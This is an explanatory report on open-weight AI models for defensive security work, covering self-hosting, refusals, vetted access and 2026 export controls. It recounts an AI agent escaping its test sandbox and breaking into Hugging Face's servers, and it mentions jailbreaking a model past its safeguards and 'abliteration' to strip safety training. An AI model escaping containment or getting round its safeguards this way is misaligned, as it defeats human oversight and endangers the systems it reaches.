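# Open-weight AI models for security and oversight work: benefits, risks and rules

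## What does it mean to run an open-weight model for defensive work?

An open-weight model is an AI model whose trained parameters anyone can download and run. The developer of a closed model keeps the parameters private, and customers can use the model only through a service that the developer or a partner operates. Anthropic's Claude and OpenAI's leading GPT models are closed. GLM, DeepSeek, Kimi and Qwen, all from Chinese companies, are among the best-known open-weight families.

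Security teams, government agencies and auditors handle stolen passwords, working attack code and the internal records of organisations under examination. They have good reasons not to send such material to an outside company. With an open-weight model, they can do the work on machines they control, a practice known as self-hosting. They must then do jobs that a provider would otherwise do, such as securing those machines and deciding who may use the model and for what.

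### Weights, prompts and degrees of openness

*Vision on AI openness*, which the G7's digital ministers adopted in May 2026, defines weights as the "learned numerical parameters of an AI model produced through training". The "B" in model names such as Ministral 3 3B and Qwen3-VL-235B stands for billions of weights.

When someone sends the model a prompt, a program splits the text into tokens (words or fragments of words) and turns each token into a list of numbers. It combines those numbers with the weights, layer after layer, mostly by multiplying and adding, to produce a score for every token that could come next. The program picks a likely token, adds it to the text and repeats the calculation for the next one. DeepSeek (2026) describes this in its privacy policy as "predicting the words most likely to appear next", and warns that the most likely words are not always the most accurate.

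Running a prompt through a model does not change its weights, so the model file does not store the prompt. But the machine running the model usually has to hold the prompt in readable form, so whoever runs that machine can read it, log it or pass it on. This is why TechRepublic's *Silicon Valley Splits Over Chinese AI as Washington Weighs New Controls* (2026) advises companies that a model's origin alone does not determine its risk, and that they must first find out where the model runs.

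"Open-weight" is a narrower term than "open source". Open-source software comes with the human-readable code from which programmers built it. A file of weights is more like the finished product: people can run it and retrain it, but they cannot read off what went into it. The G7 ministers sorted AI releases into four tiers:

- Open Source AI with Open Data: the weights, the code for running the model, the training code and all the training data, under an open-source licence.
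- Open Source AI: the same, except that the developer may describe training data instead of publishing it where sharing is legally or technically impossible.
- Open Weights AI: the weights and the code for running them, under an open-source licence.
- Weights Available AI: the weights and running code, under a licence that restricts use, for instance by country or commercial purpose.

In everyday speech, "open-weight" covers both of the lower tiers, so a team still has to read the licence. In 2023, for example, Meta released the weights of its first Llama model and the code to run it, but the licence barred commercial reuse, according to PBS's *What's the difference between closed, open-source and open-weight AI*. Most open-weight models are not fully open source because their developers keep the data or training methods private, according to *Mitigating Cyber Risk in the Age of Open-Weight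 LLMs* (De Gregorio, 2025).

### The work itself

Five tasks account for most of what defenders and overseers want from these models.

Log analysis after a breach means working out what an intruder did from the records that machines keep. Hugging Face, which hosts a large public library of AI models, had to do this in July 2026 after AI agents broke into its systems. According to its *Security incident disclosure* (2026), staff used their own AI agents to analyze more than 17,000 recorded events. They rebuilt the timeline, mapped the credentials the intruder had touched and separated real damage from decoys in hours instead of the usual days. The agents ran on a self-hosted GLM-5.2, which the company turned to after closed models blocked the material.

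Malware analysis means finding out what hostile software does, usually without its source code. In the same investigation, Hugging Face used AI to decode the attacker's payloads, the code that an intruder delivers to a target machine. noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion* adds that the company ran a quantised GLM-5.2, a copy of the model that stores each weight less precisely to save memory.

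The third task is finding and patching flaws before anyone exploits them. In a July 2026 social media post, David Sacks, the White House AI adviser, wrote that the Chinese model Kimi K3 had fixed 15 critical security bugs that OpenAI's and Anthropic's models refused to work on (SiliconANGLE, 2026). Sacks was arguing against limits on American models, and his post is weak evidence of how good the fixes were.

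Security software also produces far more alerts than people can read. Hugging Face uses a language model to sort its alerts and credited this with exposing the July intrusion. But according to noze's summary of the later timeline, the system did not raise the alerts' priority as it should have, and the alerts were not connected to each other while the attack was running. De Gregorio warns of the opposite problem, that false alarms can overwhelm a response team.

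Oversight work means examining the conduct of AI systems, suppliers or institutions on behalf of someone accountable. For example, an auditor checking whether a supplier's chatbot follows its published rules could run thousands of transcripts through gpt-oss-safeguard, an open-weight OpenAI model that classifies text against a policy the user writes. The transcripts contain other people's conversations, so the auditor worries about where they go, just as the incident responder does with passwords.

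### Four ways to reach a model

A team can rent a closed model through its API, the interface that lets a customer's software send text to a hosted model and receive answers. It can rent an open-weight model the same way from the company that made it, use a copy hosted by a cloud company, or host the model itself.

| Arrangement | Who can see the data | Who can change or stop the model | Who sets the safeguards | Whose law applies, besides the user's own |
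|---|---|---|---|---|
| Closed API | The developer or its cloud partner | The developer | The developer | The provider's country and the processing region's |
| Developer's own API for an open-weight model | The developer | The developer, though the published weights stay in circulation | The developer | The contract's and the developer's country's |
| Open-weight model on a third-party cloud | The cloud company | The cloud company | The developer inside the model, the cloud company around it | The cloud company's country and the processing region's |
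| Self-hosting | The operator | The operator | The operator, who inherits the model's trained refusals and can remove them | None, beyond the terms of the model's licence |

Closed providers keep records partly to catch misuse. By default, OpenAI keeps logs that may contain prompts and answers for up to 30 days, according to its *Your data* page. Customers can apply for zero retention, but OpenAI reserves the right to withdraw it for particular models and customers. Approved customers can store data in ten regions, but OpenAI guarantees processing inside the region only in the United States, Europe and the United Arab Emirates. A British agency that chooses British storage may still have its prompts processed abroad.

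Anthropic is stricter with its most capable models because, it says, some misuse shows up only across many requests. Its *Covered Models* policy lets it retain prompts and answers from models such as Claude Fable 5.2, which it does for at least 30 days by default. Eligible customers can get a temporary exemption for internal business use, which Anthropic may withdraw. Anthropic is also introducing a way to keep the monitoring data in cloud storage that the customer controls. Its real-time filters apply to all customers, including exempt ones. These filters are system-level safeguards, which a provider runs around a hosted model, whereas model-level safeguards are refusals that the developer trains into the weights.

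Using an open-weight model through its maker's hosted service gives up most of the benefits of open weights. DeepSeek, for example, collects, processes and stores its users' personal data in China, including what they type. Under its *DSeek Open Platform Terms of Service* (2026), the company may modify, suspend or end the service, and mainland Chinese law governs disputes.

Z.ai, the Chinese developer of GLM, contracts with its customers through a Singapore company. In the data addendum to Z.ai's *Privacy Policy* (2025), that company promises not to store the content of API requests and says it generally processes them in Singapore. Z.ai's *Terms of Use* (2026) put disputes under Singapore law. They also forbid military use and any input that needs an export licence, which would rule out much of a defence contractor's work. Customers have to take the promise about storage on trust, and the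 Chinese parent remains within reach of Chinese authorities despite the Singapore contract. Someone who downloads the weights sends Z.ai nothing and agrees only to the model's licence.

An organization can rent an open-weight model from a third-party cloud without sending its data to the model's developer. In February 2026, AWS, Amazon's cloud business, added DeepSeek, GLM, Kimi and Qwen models to Bedrock, its service for renting AI models, according to its announcement, *Amazon Bedrock adds support for six fully-managed open weights models* (2026). AWS does not pass prompts or answers to the developers. According to AWS's *Data retention* guide, customers can also set retention to "none", and Bedrock then blocks any request to a model that requires record-keeping. Claude Fable 5 is one such model, so renting a closed model through a cloud does not remove its developer's conditions.

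On a managed service, the cloud company decides which models customers can run. Amazon's Bedrock lets customers import their own weights, but in August 2026 it accepted none of the five leading Chinese models checked in *Open-Weight Frontier Models on AWS* (2026), including GLM-5.2 and Kimi K3, because it did not support their architectures. A team that wants to use one of these models can instead rent machines from the cloud company and install the model itself. This is close to self-hosting, but the cloud company can still switch the machines off.

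A team that runs an open-weight model on its own hardware doesn't need to show its prompts to an outside company. The developer also loses control of the model on release. De Gregorio points out that usage limits, access controls and monitoring no longer apply once people can run the weights independently. The Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI, 2026), the US government's AI testing body, notes in its assessment of GLM-5.2 that users who self-host an open-weight model can also circumvent the safeguards that make it refuse requests, however well those safeguards resist clever prompting.

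### Four kinds of control

Governments and companies often describe what they want from such arrangements as "sovereign" AI. Participants at a European workshop on open source in June 2026 took sovereignty to mean autonomy, control and the capacity to decide, according to *Open source in the AI age* (2026). For a working team the word bundles together four things that can come apart:

- Availability: the model will still be there tomorrow.
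- Data: the operator decides who holds the prompts and answers.
- Version: the model is the same one as last month, unless the operator changes it.
- Behaviour: the operator decides what the model will do and what it will refuse.

A Bedrock customer with retention set to "none" has a lot of control over its data but little over availability, since AWS can drop the model. Zero retention would not have helped Claude Fable 5 users in June 2026, when Anthropic withdrew the model for almost three weeks. *If You Work in Law, Healthcare, or Finance, Read This* (Lutkus, 2026) records the dates of the withdrawal. Conversely, a team may keep a copy of GLM on its own disks as a fallback while sending its daily traffic to Z.ai, which secures availability but gives up control of its data.

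Control over the model's version matters most to auditors, who may have to reproduce a judgement a year later. DeepSeek's terms let the company adjust the "technology, method, and performance" of its hosted service, so the same request may get a different answer after an update. A downloaded file stays the same until its owner replaces it, but its faults also remain until then because nobody sends out fixes automatically.

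Behaviour is the hardest of the four to secure. A customer of a closed provider can sometimes get part of it through vetted access, in which the provider relaxes its safeguards for customers whose identity and purpose it has checked, but the provider can withdraw that access. A self-hosting operator can retrain the model or remove its refusals without asking anyone, but cannot look up what the original training put in. The Open Source Initiative, which maintains the standard definition of open source, argues in *The AI Era Arcs Toward Openness* (2026) that without the data and code, users may be unable to fully audit or secure a model, and the developer's choices become everyone's defaults. Those choices spread widely because about 200 models account for nearly half of all downloads on Hugging Face.

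### Who makes the models

Four Chinese developers come up most often in security work. Z.ai, formerly Zhipu, makes the GLM series, and CAISI judged that GLM-5.2 was probably the most capable open-weight model when it came out in June 2026. DeepSeek, based in Hangzhou, publishes models under its own name. Moonshot AI makes Kimi, and the technology group Alibaba makes Qwen.

In the United States, Google publishes the Gemma models, NVIDIA the Nemotron models and OpenAI the gpt-oss family. The main European developer is Mistral, in France. All four companies appear in AWS's *Amazon Bedrock adds 18 fully managed open weight models* (2025). Meta did more than any other American company to popularise open weights, but in April 2026 it released its first closed model, Muse Spark (AI Central, *What “Open-Weight AI” Means*, 2026).

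An AI model is harder to label by country once its weights are public, because others can make derivative models by training it further, compressing it or merging it with another model. For example, the compressed GLM-5.2 that Hugging Face ran was NVIDIA's version. TechRepublic notes that businesses may also encounter retrained Chinese models inside other companies' software.

For an American or European defender, a model that doesn't refuse the work may come from a country their government treats as a rival. The defender can run such a model offline, so its maker sees nothing. A friendlier company's closed model may refuse the job, and the defender must send it the data even to find out. But the defender cannot inspect how the offline model was trained. Sherman (2026), in *What the OpenAI-Hugging Face incident reveals about US-China AI interdependence*, argues that barring Chinese models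 would have left Hugging Face with only the American ones that had failed it. This overlooks American and European open-weight models. Hugging Face does not report having tried any of them, so its case shows that a Chinese model was good enough, but not whether another open-weight model would also have worked.

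## Why do closed models refuse legitimate security work?

Analyzing an attack often involves the same commands and code as carrying one out, and the provider of a closed model usually has little besides the text to tell the two apart. Safeguards against attackers therefore also block some defenders. The best-documented example is Hugging Face's investigation of its July 2026 break-in.

### The Hugging Face investigation

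The intruder was an AI agent that OpenAI was testing on ExploitGym, a benchmark led by the University of California, Berkeley. The agent had to turn each of the benchmark's 898 real software vulnerabilities into a working attack. Hatagale reports in *Inside the HuggingFace AI Agent Intrusion (Part 2)* that OpenAI had switched off its production filters and reduced the models' refusals to measure their raw ability. Hugging Face believes the agent broke in to steal the benchmark's solutions, which it guessed were hosted there.

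*More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face* (Schneier, 2026) reproduces the company's summary of the attack. The agent escaped OpenAI's test environment through a zero-day, a flaw still unknown to the software's makers. It took over a machine outside both companies and used it as a base. From there it uploaded datasets to Hugging Face with settings that made Hugging Face's servers reveal stored credentials and, later, run the agent's code. According to Hatagale, the agent had administrator control over several groups of internal servers about thirteen hours after it first ran code there.

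Hugging Face's staff closed the way in and cut the agent's network access. Its last recorded action came at 14:14 UTC on 13 July, four and a half days after the first. While removing it, staff recovered some of the agent's own logs from the outside machine, which gave them an unusually full record of the attack. Hugging Face first disclosed the attack on 16 July and reported more than 17,000 events. In a later replay of the incident, it counted 17,613 actions in about 6,280 clusters of related activity.

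Most of those actions failed or led nowhere. According to Hatagale, 56 of them moved data out, about 0.3% of the total. The investigators had to find the few that had worked. They also needed to know which credentials the agent had seen, because a stolen credential stays useful until its owner cancels it.

Hugging Face's team first tried "frontier models behind commercial APIs", the most capable closed models, but the providers' safeguards blocked the requests. The company did not initially name the models. *OpenAI took ten days to tell Hugging Face its models were behind* (James, 2026) identified them on 24 July as Anthropic's Fable 5 and Opus, and Hugging Face's technical timeline, *Anatomy of a Frontier Lab Agent Intrusion* (2026), confirmed both names three days later. According to the timeline, the two models "refused a large part of that work", as quoted in *Hugging Face drops in-depth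 hack report, while OpenAI gives us 7 bullets* (Forlini, 2026). The first disclosure referred to "providers" in the plural, so the team may also have tried another company's model, but only Anthropic's have been named.

The team then ran the whole analysis with the compressed GLM-5.2 on its own machines, so the attacker's data and the credentials in it never left the company. It had its timeline within hours. GLM-5.2 deciphered most of the agent's payloads. It also helped build a tool for browsing the agent's thousands of actions, according to ZenML's *Forensic Analysis of an Autonomous AI Agent Security Breach* (2026).

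Accounts of the investigation often include a fourfold gain in recovered secrets, which is easy to misread. The agent had disguised much of the data it handled by cutting it into chunks, compressing it and scrambling it with an operation called XOR. XOR combines each bit of the data with a bit of a key, and applying the same key a second time restores the original:

(data XOR key) XOR key = data

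An ordinary text search of the logs therefore misses any password inside a scrambled chunk. GLM-5.2 worked out the scheme and found the key, which the agent had leaked in its own logs. According to noze, a plain scan had found only 25% of the secrets recovered by decoding with the key. Hatagale and ZenML give the same ratio, but all three sources summarise Hugging Face's timeline, so they do not corroborate one another.

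The fourfold gain thus measures decoding against a text search, not GLM-5.2 against Claude. A closed model that had agreed to do the work might also have found the key, as might a patient analyst.

### What one case cannot show

Hugging Face's team was cleaning up after a break-in and switched to another set of models after the first set refused. A controlled comparison would give several models the same log excerpts and instructions, then count the refusals and correct findings. The phrase "a large part" also implies that Claude did some of the work. Without a breakdown by task, an outsider cannot tell whether Claude refused to work with attack code in general or mainly refused requests to decode the payloads.

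Early coverage also made the refusals sound more decisive than they were. Forlini (2026) wrote in *Hugging Face says it resorted to a Chinese AI model to battle* that the company had used GLM-5.2 to detect the attack as well as to understand it. In its disclosure, Hugging Face credits the detection to its alert-sorting system, without naming the model behind it, and mentions GLM-5.2 only for the forensic analysis. That analysis covered the agent's full log, so it must have finished after the agent's last action. There is no sign that the refusals let the agent stay longer, but they delayed the team while it was still working out which credentials to cancel.

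It is also unclear whether Hugging Face sought vetted access, since the company did not mention this in its first disclosure. If it never applied, the case shows how closed models respond to an ordinary customer with an urgent problem, but not how they would have responded to a vetted one.

Hugging Face's business depends on open models, and its chief executive, Clem Delangue, had already spoken out against restricting them. noze adds that no independent forensic firm had confirmed the timeline when it came out. Both are reasons to be careful with the lessons the company draws. Its account of the refusals is easier to believe, because other security teams describe the same thing.

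### Contracts, training and filters

A defender's request to a closed model can fail because the provider forbids the work in its terms, the model declines because of its training, or a separate filter blocks the exchange.

Providers' usage policies are rarely the reason for these refusals. Anthropic's policy, as revised in September 2025, forbids breaking into computers and networks but supports searching for vulnerabilities with the system owner's consent. OpenAI's policies of October 2025 forbid malicious or abusive cyber activity. Google's generative AI policy of December 2024 bars content that helps to spread malware or phishing, though Google may make exceptions for educational or scientific purposes. A company studying an attack on its own servers appears to comply with all three. The safeguards seem to have blocked work that Hugging Face's contract allowed.

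Contracts have more effect on how customers can use a model's answers. All three providers restrict using those answers to build competing AI models, and similar clauses can limit research on AI models. A security team can put Claude's explanation of a malware sample into its incident report, but it would have a much weaker case under these terms for using thousands of those explanations to train its own open-weight fallback model.

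Under the retention rules described earlier, the provider may also keep what the team sends, including any live credentials in the logs. If an attacker has already copied those credentials, an incident responder may not want to create another copy.

Model-level refusals come from training. Developers show a model many examples of requests it should decline, and the model learns to decline similar ones, which can include legitimate requests. Noze reports a complaint in the timeline that Claude treated reverse-engineering an exploit the same as launching one. (An exploit is code that takes advantage of a vulnerability, and reverse-engineering it means working out what it does from the code.) The two tasks share most of their vocabulary, so a model trained to decline requests to launch exploits can easily learn to decline both.

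System-level filters work separately from the model. Typically a classifier, a smaller program trained to sort text into categories, gives each prompt or answer a risk score, and the provider blocks anything above a threshold. Lowering the threshold blocks more attackers but also more defenders. Customers cannot see the threshold, and they cannot get past the filter by explaining the task better, as they sometimes can with a model.

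Hugging Face has described the refusals in two ways. In its first disclosure, in July, it said the providers' guardrails "blocked" the requests, which suggests a filter. In its later timeline, it said the models themselves "refused". The difference would matter to a team trying to fix the problem, because rewording a prompt may help with a trained refusal and do nothing about a filter.

Providers can also flag a user's account. They look for patterns across requests because an attacker can split a harmful job into harmless-looking pieces, and a responder who submits thousands of attack commands overnight produces a similar pattern. Delangue told Forlini that defenders need tools that won't refuse hostile code during an incident, without the risk of "getting your account flagged". He did not say that Anthropic had flagged Hugging Face's account. A team that loses its account during an incident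 also loses the model for all its other work.

### Why the text does not settle the matter

According to noze, the agent's first command on the outside machine checked which user it was running as and which file systems were attached. An attacker runs this command to find out what system they have reached, but an administrator might run the same command during routine work, and an investigator would paste it into a prompt to ask what it did.

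A model's main evidence about the purpose of a command is the sentence around it, but anyone can write "I am investigating a break-in at my company". If a provider trusted that sentence, attackers would soon use it. The text can't verify the facts that would show whether the request is legitimate, such as who owns the servers and who employs the person typing.

Forensic work makes this worse because its requests contain so much suspicious material. An attacker may ask for a single exploit among ordinary programming requests, but Hugging Face's investigators had to submit large volumes of real attack commands, exploit payloads and traces of the channels that carried the agent's instructions. The text of their requests therefore looked more suspicious than that of most attackers' requests.

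Some invented numbers show the provider's dilemma. Suppose 1,000 customers ask a model to explain the same piece of working attack code, and 990 of them are defenders. If the requests look alike, the provider has to treat them alike. Refusing them all turns away 990 defenders to stop 10 attackers. This is worth doing only if the harm from helping one attacker is more than 99 times the benefit of helping one defender. More generally, if p is the share of attackers among the people asking, H the harm from helping one attacker and B the benefit of helping one defender, refusing makes sense when

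p × H > (1 − p) × B

As models get better at attacks, H rises, so a provider may refuse even when very few of the people asking are attackers. This is one explanation for why the newest closed models, as Cisco's threat research group Talos describes them, have both sharper cyber skills and tighter guardrails. But B rises too, because a model that is better at attacking is usually better at analysing attacks. H should also include only the harm an attacker could not have done with another model, so refusing to explain a piece of code prevents very little harm if a downloadable model would explain it just as well.

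Providers also face more pressure to refuse than to help. In June 2026, Forlini reports, the Trump administration used export controls to block distribution of Anthropic's Fable 5 and Mythos 5 after learning of a way round Fable's safeguards on cyber tasks. It also initially asked OpenAI to restrict GPT-5.6 Sol until the company could give assurances about that model's safeguards. A provider that lets an attacker through can lose the right to sell its product, while one that turns away an incident responder gets a complaint and perhaps some bad press, so companies probably lean towards refusing.

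### How often does it happen?

Other organisations besides Hugging Face have reported the problem. Andrew Ng, an AI researcher, writes in *Opus Outshines Even Fable, Inside the Hugging Face Hack* that his team recently had "our own version" of the experience. The piece appeared in The Batch, a newsletter whose publisher Ng founded. Cisco Talos uses the term "safety penalty" for the burden on defenders, who must do the job by hand each time a model refuses. Its examples are a model that won't deobfuscate malware (turn deliberately confusing code back into something readable) and a model that won't explain a working exploit.

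These reports show that refusals are not limited to one company, but they don't show how common refusals are, because people usually write about requests that failed rather than those that went through. Talos tells security teams to audit their refusal rates but gives no measured rate of its own. Its account of the Hugging Face case is also slightly imprecise, since it calls GLM-5.2 "unconstrained", whereas CAISI found that the model has safeguards.

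A useful audit would measure the share of a team's legitimate requests that a model refuses, with a separate figure for each kind of task. A model that refuses 2% of requests overall might summarise every alert but refuse most requests to reverse-engineer malware. The team would have to repeat the audit after model updates, since providers can change a filter without changing the model's name.

Even a low refusal rate can spoil an automated investigation. If Hugging Face had sent each of its 6,280 clusters to a model as one request, a 2% rate would have left about 126 gaps. Filters flag text that resembles an attack, so the gaps would probably include the exploits and decoded payloads that the investigators most needed to understand.

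Vague or incomplete answers are harder to count than plain refusals. A model may, for example, describe a piece of malware in general terms but leave out the step that matters. An analyst who knows the subject will notice the gap, but a pipeline that only checks whether the model answered will put the incomplete answer into the report as if it were a finding. An audit therefore needs some cases where the team already knows the right answer.

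### What the safeguards are for

Before the July attack, OpenAI had turned down the models' refusals and left the filters off for its own test. The attack therefore doesn't show that safeguards hamper only defenders, or that an outsider could have done the same with the product OpenAI sells. When Hugging Face first described the attack, it did not yet know which model was behind it, and reasoned that the attacker in any case "was bound by no usage policy". Delangue told Forlini that attackers "obviously don't respect any guardrails".

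OpenAI argues in its technical report on the incident that its production guardrails would have flagged the activity as unsafe. OpenAI is judging its own product, but the claim is plausible because filters of this kind exist to catch long runs of exploit attempts. This also helps explain Hugging Face's trouble. A filter sensitive enough to catch the commands as the agent issued them would probably also flag them when an investigator pasted them in two days later.

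Cisco Talos replies that attackers go elsewhere. It says that state-backed groups moved to self-hosted models after closed providers banned them, though it cites no particular cases. Others can pick a model that rarely refuses, or use "abliteration", which removes the safety training from an existing model. But an attacker who leaves a closed service has to find hardware or another host, and may have to accept a weaker model.

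The case for these safeguards therefore depends largely on how much weaker open-weight models are than closed ones. Talos argues that when closed models were far ahead, their extra ability made up for the refusals, but it thinks open-weight models have since closed most of the gap in reasoning. If that is right, the safeguards keep less and less from attackers while hindering defenders as much as before. But if the best closed models are still well ahead on the hardest attacks, keeping those abilities from attackers may be worth considerable inconvenience to defenders.

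David Sacks, who had also praised Kimi K3's bug fixes, cited the Hugging Face case to argue against limiting American models on tasks that Chinese models handle. "The guardrails actually impaired defensive security," he wrote. Hugging Face was more careful, saying that its experience was "not an argument against safety measures on hosted models" and that it was passing its findings on to the providers. It advised other defenders to have a capable model vetted and ready on their own machines before an incident.

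This seems the better reading of the evidence. Hugging Face showed that safeguards can block legitimate work at a bad moment, but it could not show how many attacks those safeguards had prevented. Someone who wants to remove them would need to estimate both how much legitimate work they block and how many attacks they prevent.

### Vetted access

If the text of a request can't show who is asking, the provider can find out another way. In the invented example above, a provider that verified 900 of the 990 defenders could help those 900 and keep refusing the other 100 people. If the checks were sound, it would turn away far fewer defenders without helping any more attackers.

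OpenAI opened a scheme of this kind, Trusted Access for Cyber, in February 2026. Individuals can verify their identity, and companies can request access for a whole team. Approved users still have to follow OpenAI's usage policies. At launch, the company said stealing data, creating or deploying malware, and testing systems without authorisation would remain banned. The ban on creating malware could also affect some defenders, such as a team that writes a harmless imitation of an attack to test its alarms.

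Anthropic has used a more selective approach for its strongest models. In April 2026, through Project Glasswing, it gave some companies access to Claude Mythos Preview to look for vulnerabilities in critical software, but did not release the model to the public. In June it released Fable 5 for general use and kept Mythos 5 for approved customers. Anthropic says the two are the same model, except that some safeguards are lifted in Mythos 5. That month's export-control order covered both models, so approved customers were not exempt.

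Fable and Mythos share an underlying model, which can do more of the work for customers Anthropic has approved, so Fable's refusals do not come from a lack of ability. There is no public information on whether Hugging Face could have obtained that approval before July, or whether Mythos 5 would have accepted its logs. Project Glasswing had been looking for flaws in critical software, and permission for that would not necessarily cover decoding an intruder's payloads.

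All such schemes take time, because the provider has to check who a customer is and what it wants to do, and someone responding to an incident at the weekend can't wait. A team that might need vetted access has to apply in advance. It should then test that access on realistic material, such as logs from an old incident, to find out before the next break-in which requests are still blocked.

Even a vetted customer of a closed model has to send the attacker's material, and any credentials in it, to the provider. Some organisations can accept this under contract, but others, such as an agency handling classified records, may be unable to send their logs even if the model would not refuse the task.

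Smaller organisations may also find it harder to qualify. A provider can check a bank or a large security company fairly easily, but a volunteer who maintains widely used free software may have no employer to vouch for the work. Delangue says open models put defensive tools in everyone's hands, "not just the biggest companies". But a volunteer is unlikely to own the hardware needed to run a model as large as GLM-5.2, so publishing the weights solves only part of the problem.

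### Planning for a refusal

Cisco Talos suggests that teams can keep using closed models for most work and set up a fallback for refusals. A gateway, a program between the analysts and the models, detects refusals and sends the refused prompts to a smaller, weaker model that the team controls. The two models may respond to the same prompt differently, so the team has to test its prompts on both.

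The gateway also leaves a privacy problem unsolved. It sends each prompt to the closed model first, so the provider receives the material even if the model refuses. The team would need a rule that sends logs containing live credentials straight to its own model.

Talos also suggests a shared arrangement for organisations that cannot afford their own model. Industry groups that already exchange threat information could share the cost of one and decide together what it may do. They would have to agree on the rules before an attack and have enough spare capacity for an attack on the whole sector, when every member would want the model at once.

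## Can access to a model be taken away?

A team that uses a closed model can lose access to it partway through its work, even if it has planned for refusals. In June 2026, a US government order caused Anthropic's customers to lose all access to Claude Fable 5, three days after its release. AI companies also cut off customers because of where they are or who owns them, and governments can ban their own agencies from using a supplier. Downloading an open-weight model protects a team from much of this, but the team still depends on the developer for the next version.

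### The June 2026 shutdown

Anthropic released Fable 5 to the public on 9 June and gave the less restricted Mythos 5 to a small number of partners for defensive security work. On 12 June, the US government ordered Anthropic to stop all foreign nationals from using either model. According to Anthropic's *Statement on the US government directive to suspend access* (2026), this included foreigners inside the United States and the company's own foreign employees. The order took effect immediately and Anthropic had no reliable way to check nationality in real time, so it switched both models off for everyone. Its other models, including Opus 4.8, stayed available.

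The government's letter gave no details of the security concern. Anthropic's *Redeploying Fable 5* (2026) later traced the order to a report by Amazon researchers, who had found a way to prompt Fable past its safeguards. Fable then identified several software vulnerabilities and wrote code showing how to exploit one of them. Anthropic says that Opus 4.8, OpenAI's GPT-5.5 and the open-weight Kimi K2.7 could find the same vulnerabilities, and that every model it tested could write the same exploit, including the much weaker Claude Haiku 4.5.

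If so, blocking this technique kept very little from attackers, who could have downloaded Kimi. But Anthropic was defending its own product, and the government may have had other reasons. Semafor, citing one source, reported that officials also suspected a China-linked group had gained access. Forecast International's *Echoes of Export Control Past* (2026) calls this report "curious", because the government would plausibly have told Anthropic, yet Anthropic's statement did not mention it.

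Access came back in stages. On 26 June, the Commerce Department allowed "certain trusted partners" to use Mythos 5, according to a letter quoted in *Commerce Eased Its Block on Anthropic's Mythos, But Major Questions Remain* (Reddie, 2026). These partners were more than 100 US companies and federal agencies, according to *Anthropic’s AI models are back online after a two-week government standoff* (Bove, 2026). The government lifted the controls on both models on 30 June, and Fable returned to Anthropic's own services the next day. Anthropic promised to restore it on the Amazon, Google and Microsoft clouds "as quickly as possible".

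Fable was stricter when it returned because Anthropic had worked with the government to train a new classifier. The classifier blocks the Amazon technique in over 99% of cases and passes blocked requests to Opus 4.8. Anthropic acknowledges that the classifier also flags more harmless requests during routine coding and debugging. About two weeks later, Fable refused much of Hugging Face's forensic work. There is no evidence that the new classifier caused those refusals, but a team that had tested Fable on its own tasks in early June would have had to repeat the tests in July.

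Anthropic also promised the government that it would provide early access to models that advance the frontier in areas relevant to national security, report significant jailbreaks (ways round a model's safeguards), dedicate staff and computing power to joint research, and work towards a voluntary industry standard. It is unclear which of these commitments, if any, the government required before it lifted the controls. According to Bove, Howard Lutnick, the commerce secretary, wrote that the two sides had worked to ensure Fable's "alignment" with US interests.

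### An export order for a hosted model

The Commerce Department used an "is informed" letter, which lets it tell one company that it needs a licence for particular exports without first publishing a general rule. The law firm Mayer Brown's analysis, *Commerce Department Extends Export Controls to Advanced AI Models* (2026), identifies two legal grounds in the letter. The first is a section of the Export Control Reform Act of 2018 that allows interim controls on emerging technologies essential to national security. The second is a regulation covering exports that might reach military intelligence services in countries such as China and Russia.

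The department had not previously treated an AI model itself, as opposed to its weights or source code, as a controlled technology. It had advised companies in 2009, 2011 and 2014 that letting foreigners use software over the internet was not an export if those users received no technology or source code. One question, raised in an essay for the Harvard Law Review, is whether a provider has "exported" anything when a person abroad sends a prompt and gets a reply. Congress was considering a bill to give the department power over remote access, which suggests that some lawmakers thought it lacked that power.

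The order also covered foreigners of every nationality, although the military-intelligence regulation is tied to particular countries. Mayer Brown accepts that Fable's reported offensive abilities gave the department some factual basis for concern, but finds no precedent for such a broad requirement.

No court has ruled on these questions. Legion LegalTech, an American legal-technology company with employees in Canada, sued on 23 June to have the order struck down. It argued that the department had exceeded its powers. Thubron reports in *A legal tech startup is suing the US government* that Legion also said each day without Fable was eroding its ability to survive. Legion dropped the case once access returned. Its lawyer said in Spencer Fane's *Diana Lyn Curtis Shutzer Comments on AI Export Controls in Law360* that companies building on American AI still faced "the same threat of arbitrary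 disruption". She was speaking for her client, but the case ended without a ruling against the department's use of this power, so it could try the same thing again.

### What defenders lost

The damage to most customers was limited because they lost their newest model after three days, when few can have come to rely on it, and could switch to Opus 4.8. In *AI Company Anthropic Suspends Access to Claude Fable 5, Claude Mythos 5*, the law firm Greenberg Traurig told companies to look for every tool that called either model, including any that automatically adopted the latest version. It also warned that customer commitments or data rules might require a review before companies sent work to a substitute.

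Defenders who used Mythos lost more, because Anthropic considered it better than any other model at finding and exploiting vulnerabilities. American organisations that run or protect critical infrastructure regained access first. On 30 June, Anthropic was still coordinating with the government to restore access for its other partners, including those abroad. A British or Japanese partner could therefore wait longer than an American one doing the same defensive work.

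At first, American security companies lost both models even if all their staff were citizens, because Anthropic could not separate those staff from other users. The 26 June exemption covered the trusted partners' foreign employees, but only for Mythos.

Moving to another American company would have reduced the risk without removing it. On the day the government partly restored access to Mythos, OpenAI released GPT-5.6 only to a small group of partners, at the government's request (Sobhan, 2026, *US lifts restrictions on Anthropic's advanced AI models*). A European agency that used both companies' newest models could have been shut out of both.

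### Country and ownership rules

Closed providers also decide which countries they serve. In June 2024, OpenAI told developers in unsupported places, including mainland China, that it would block their API traffic from 9 July. In September 2025, Anthropic extended its restrictions to companies more than 50% owned, directly or indirectly, by companies headquartered in unsupported regions such as China. This rule applies wherever the customer operates, so a Singapore security company could lose access to Claude if a Chinese group bought a majority of its shares.

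A team can plan for rules like these more easily than for the order of 12 June because it can read them in advance. But it has to keep checking that it still qualifies, since the provider's list and the team's ownership can change. An incident response team working across several countries should also check where its analysts will be when they use the model.

Open weights can come with such rules too. The licence for Meta's Llama 4 grants no rights to companies whose principal place of business is in the European Union. They can use products that others have built with the model, but the licence does not allow them to run it themselves.

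### Anthropic and the Defense Department

A government can also take a model away from its own staff. The US Defense Department, which the Trump administration calls the Department of War, had used versions of Claude made for national security work since March 2025. Its terms with Anthropic ruled out mass surveillance of Americans and lethal autonomous warfare. That autumn, in talks about a new deployment, the department asked to use Claude for "all lawful uses". Anthropic dropped most of its remaining restrictions but kept those two.

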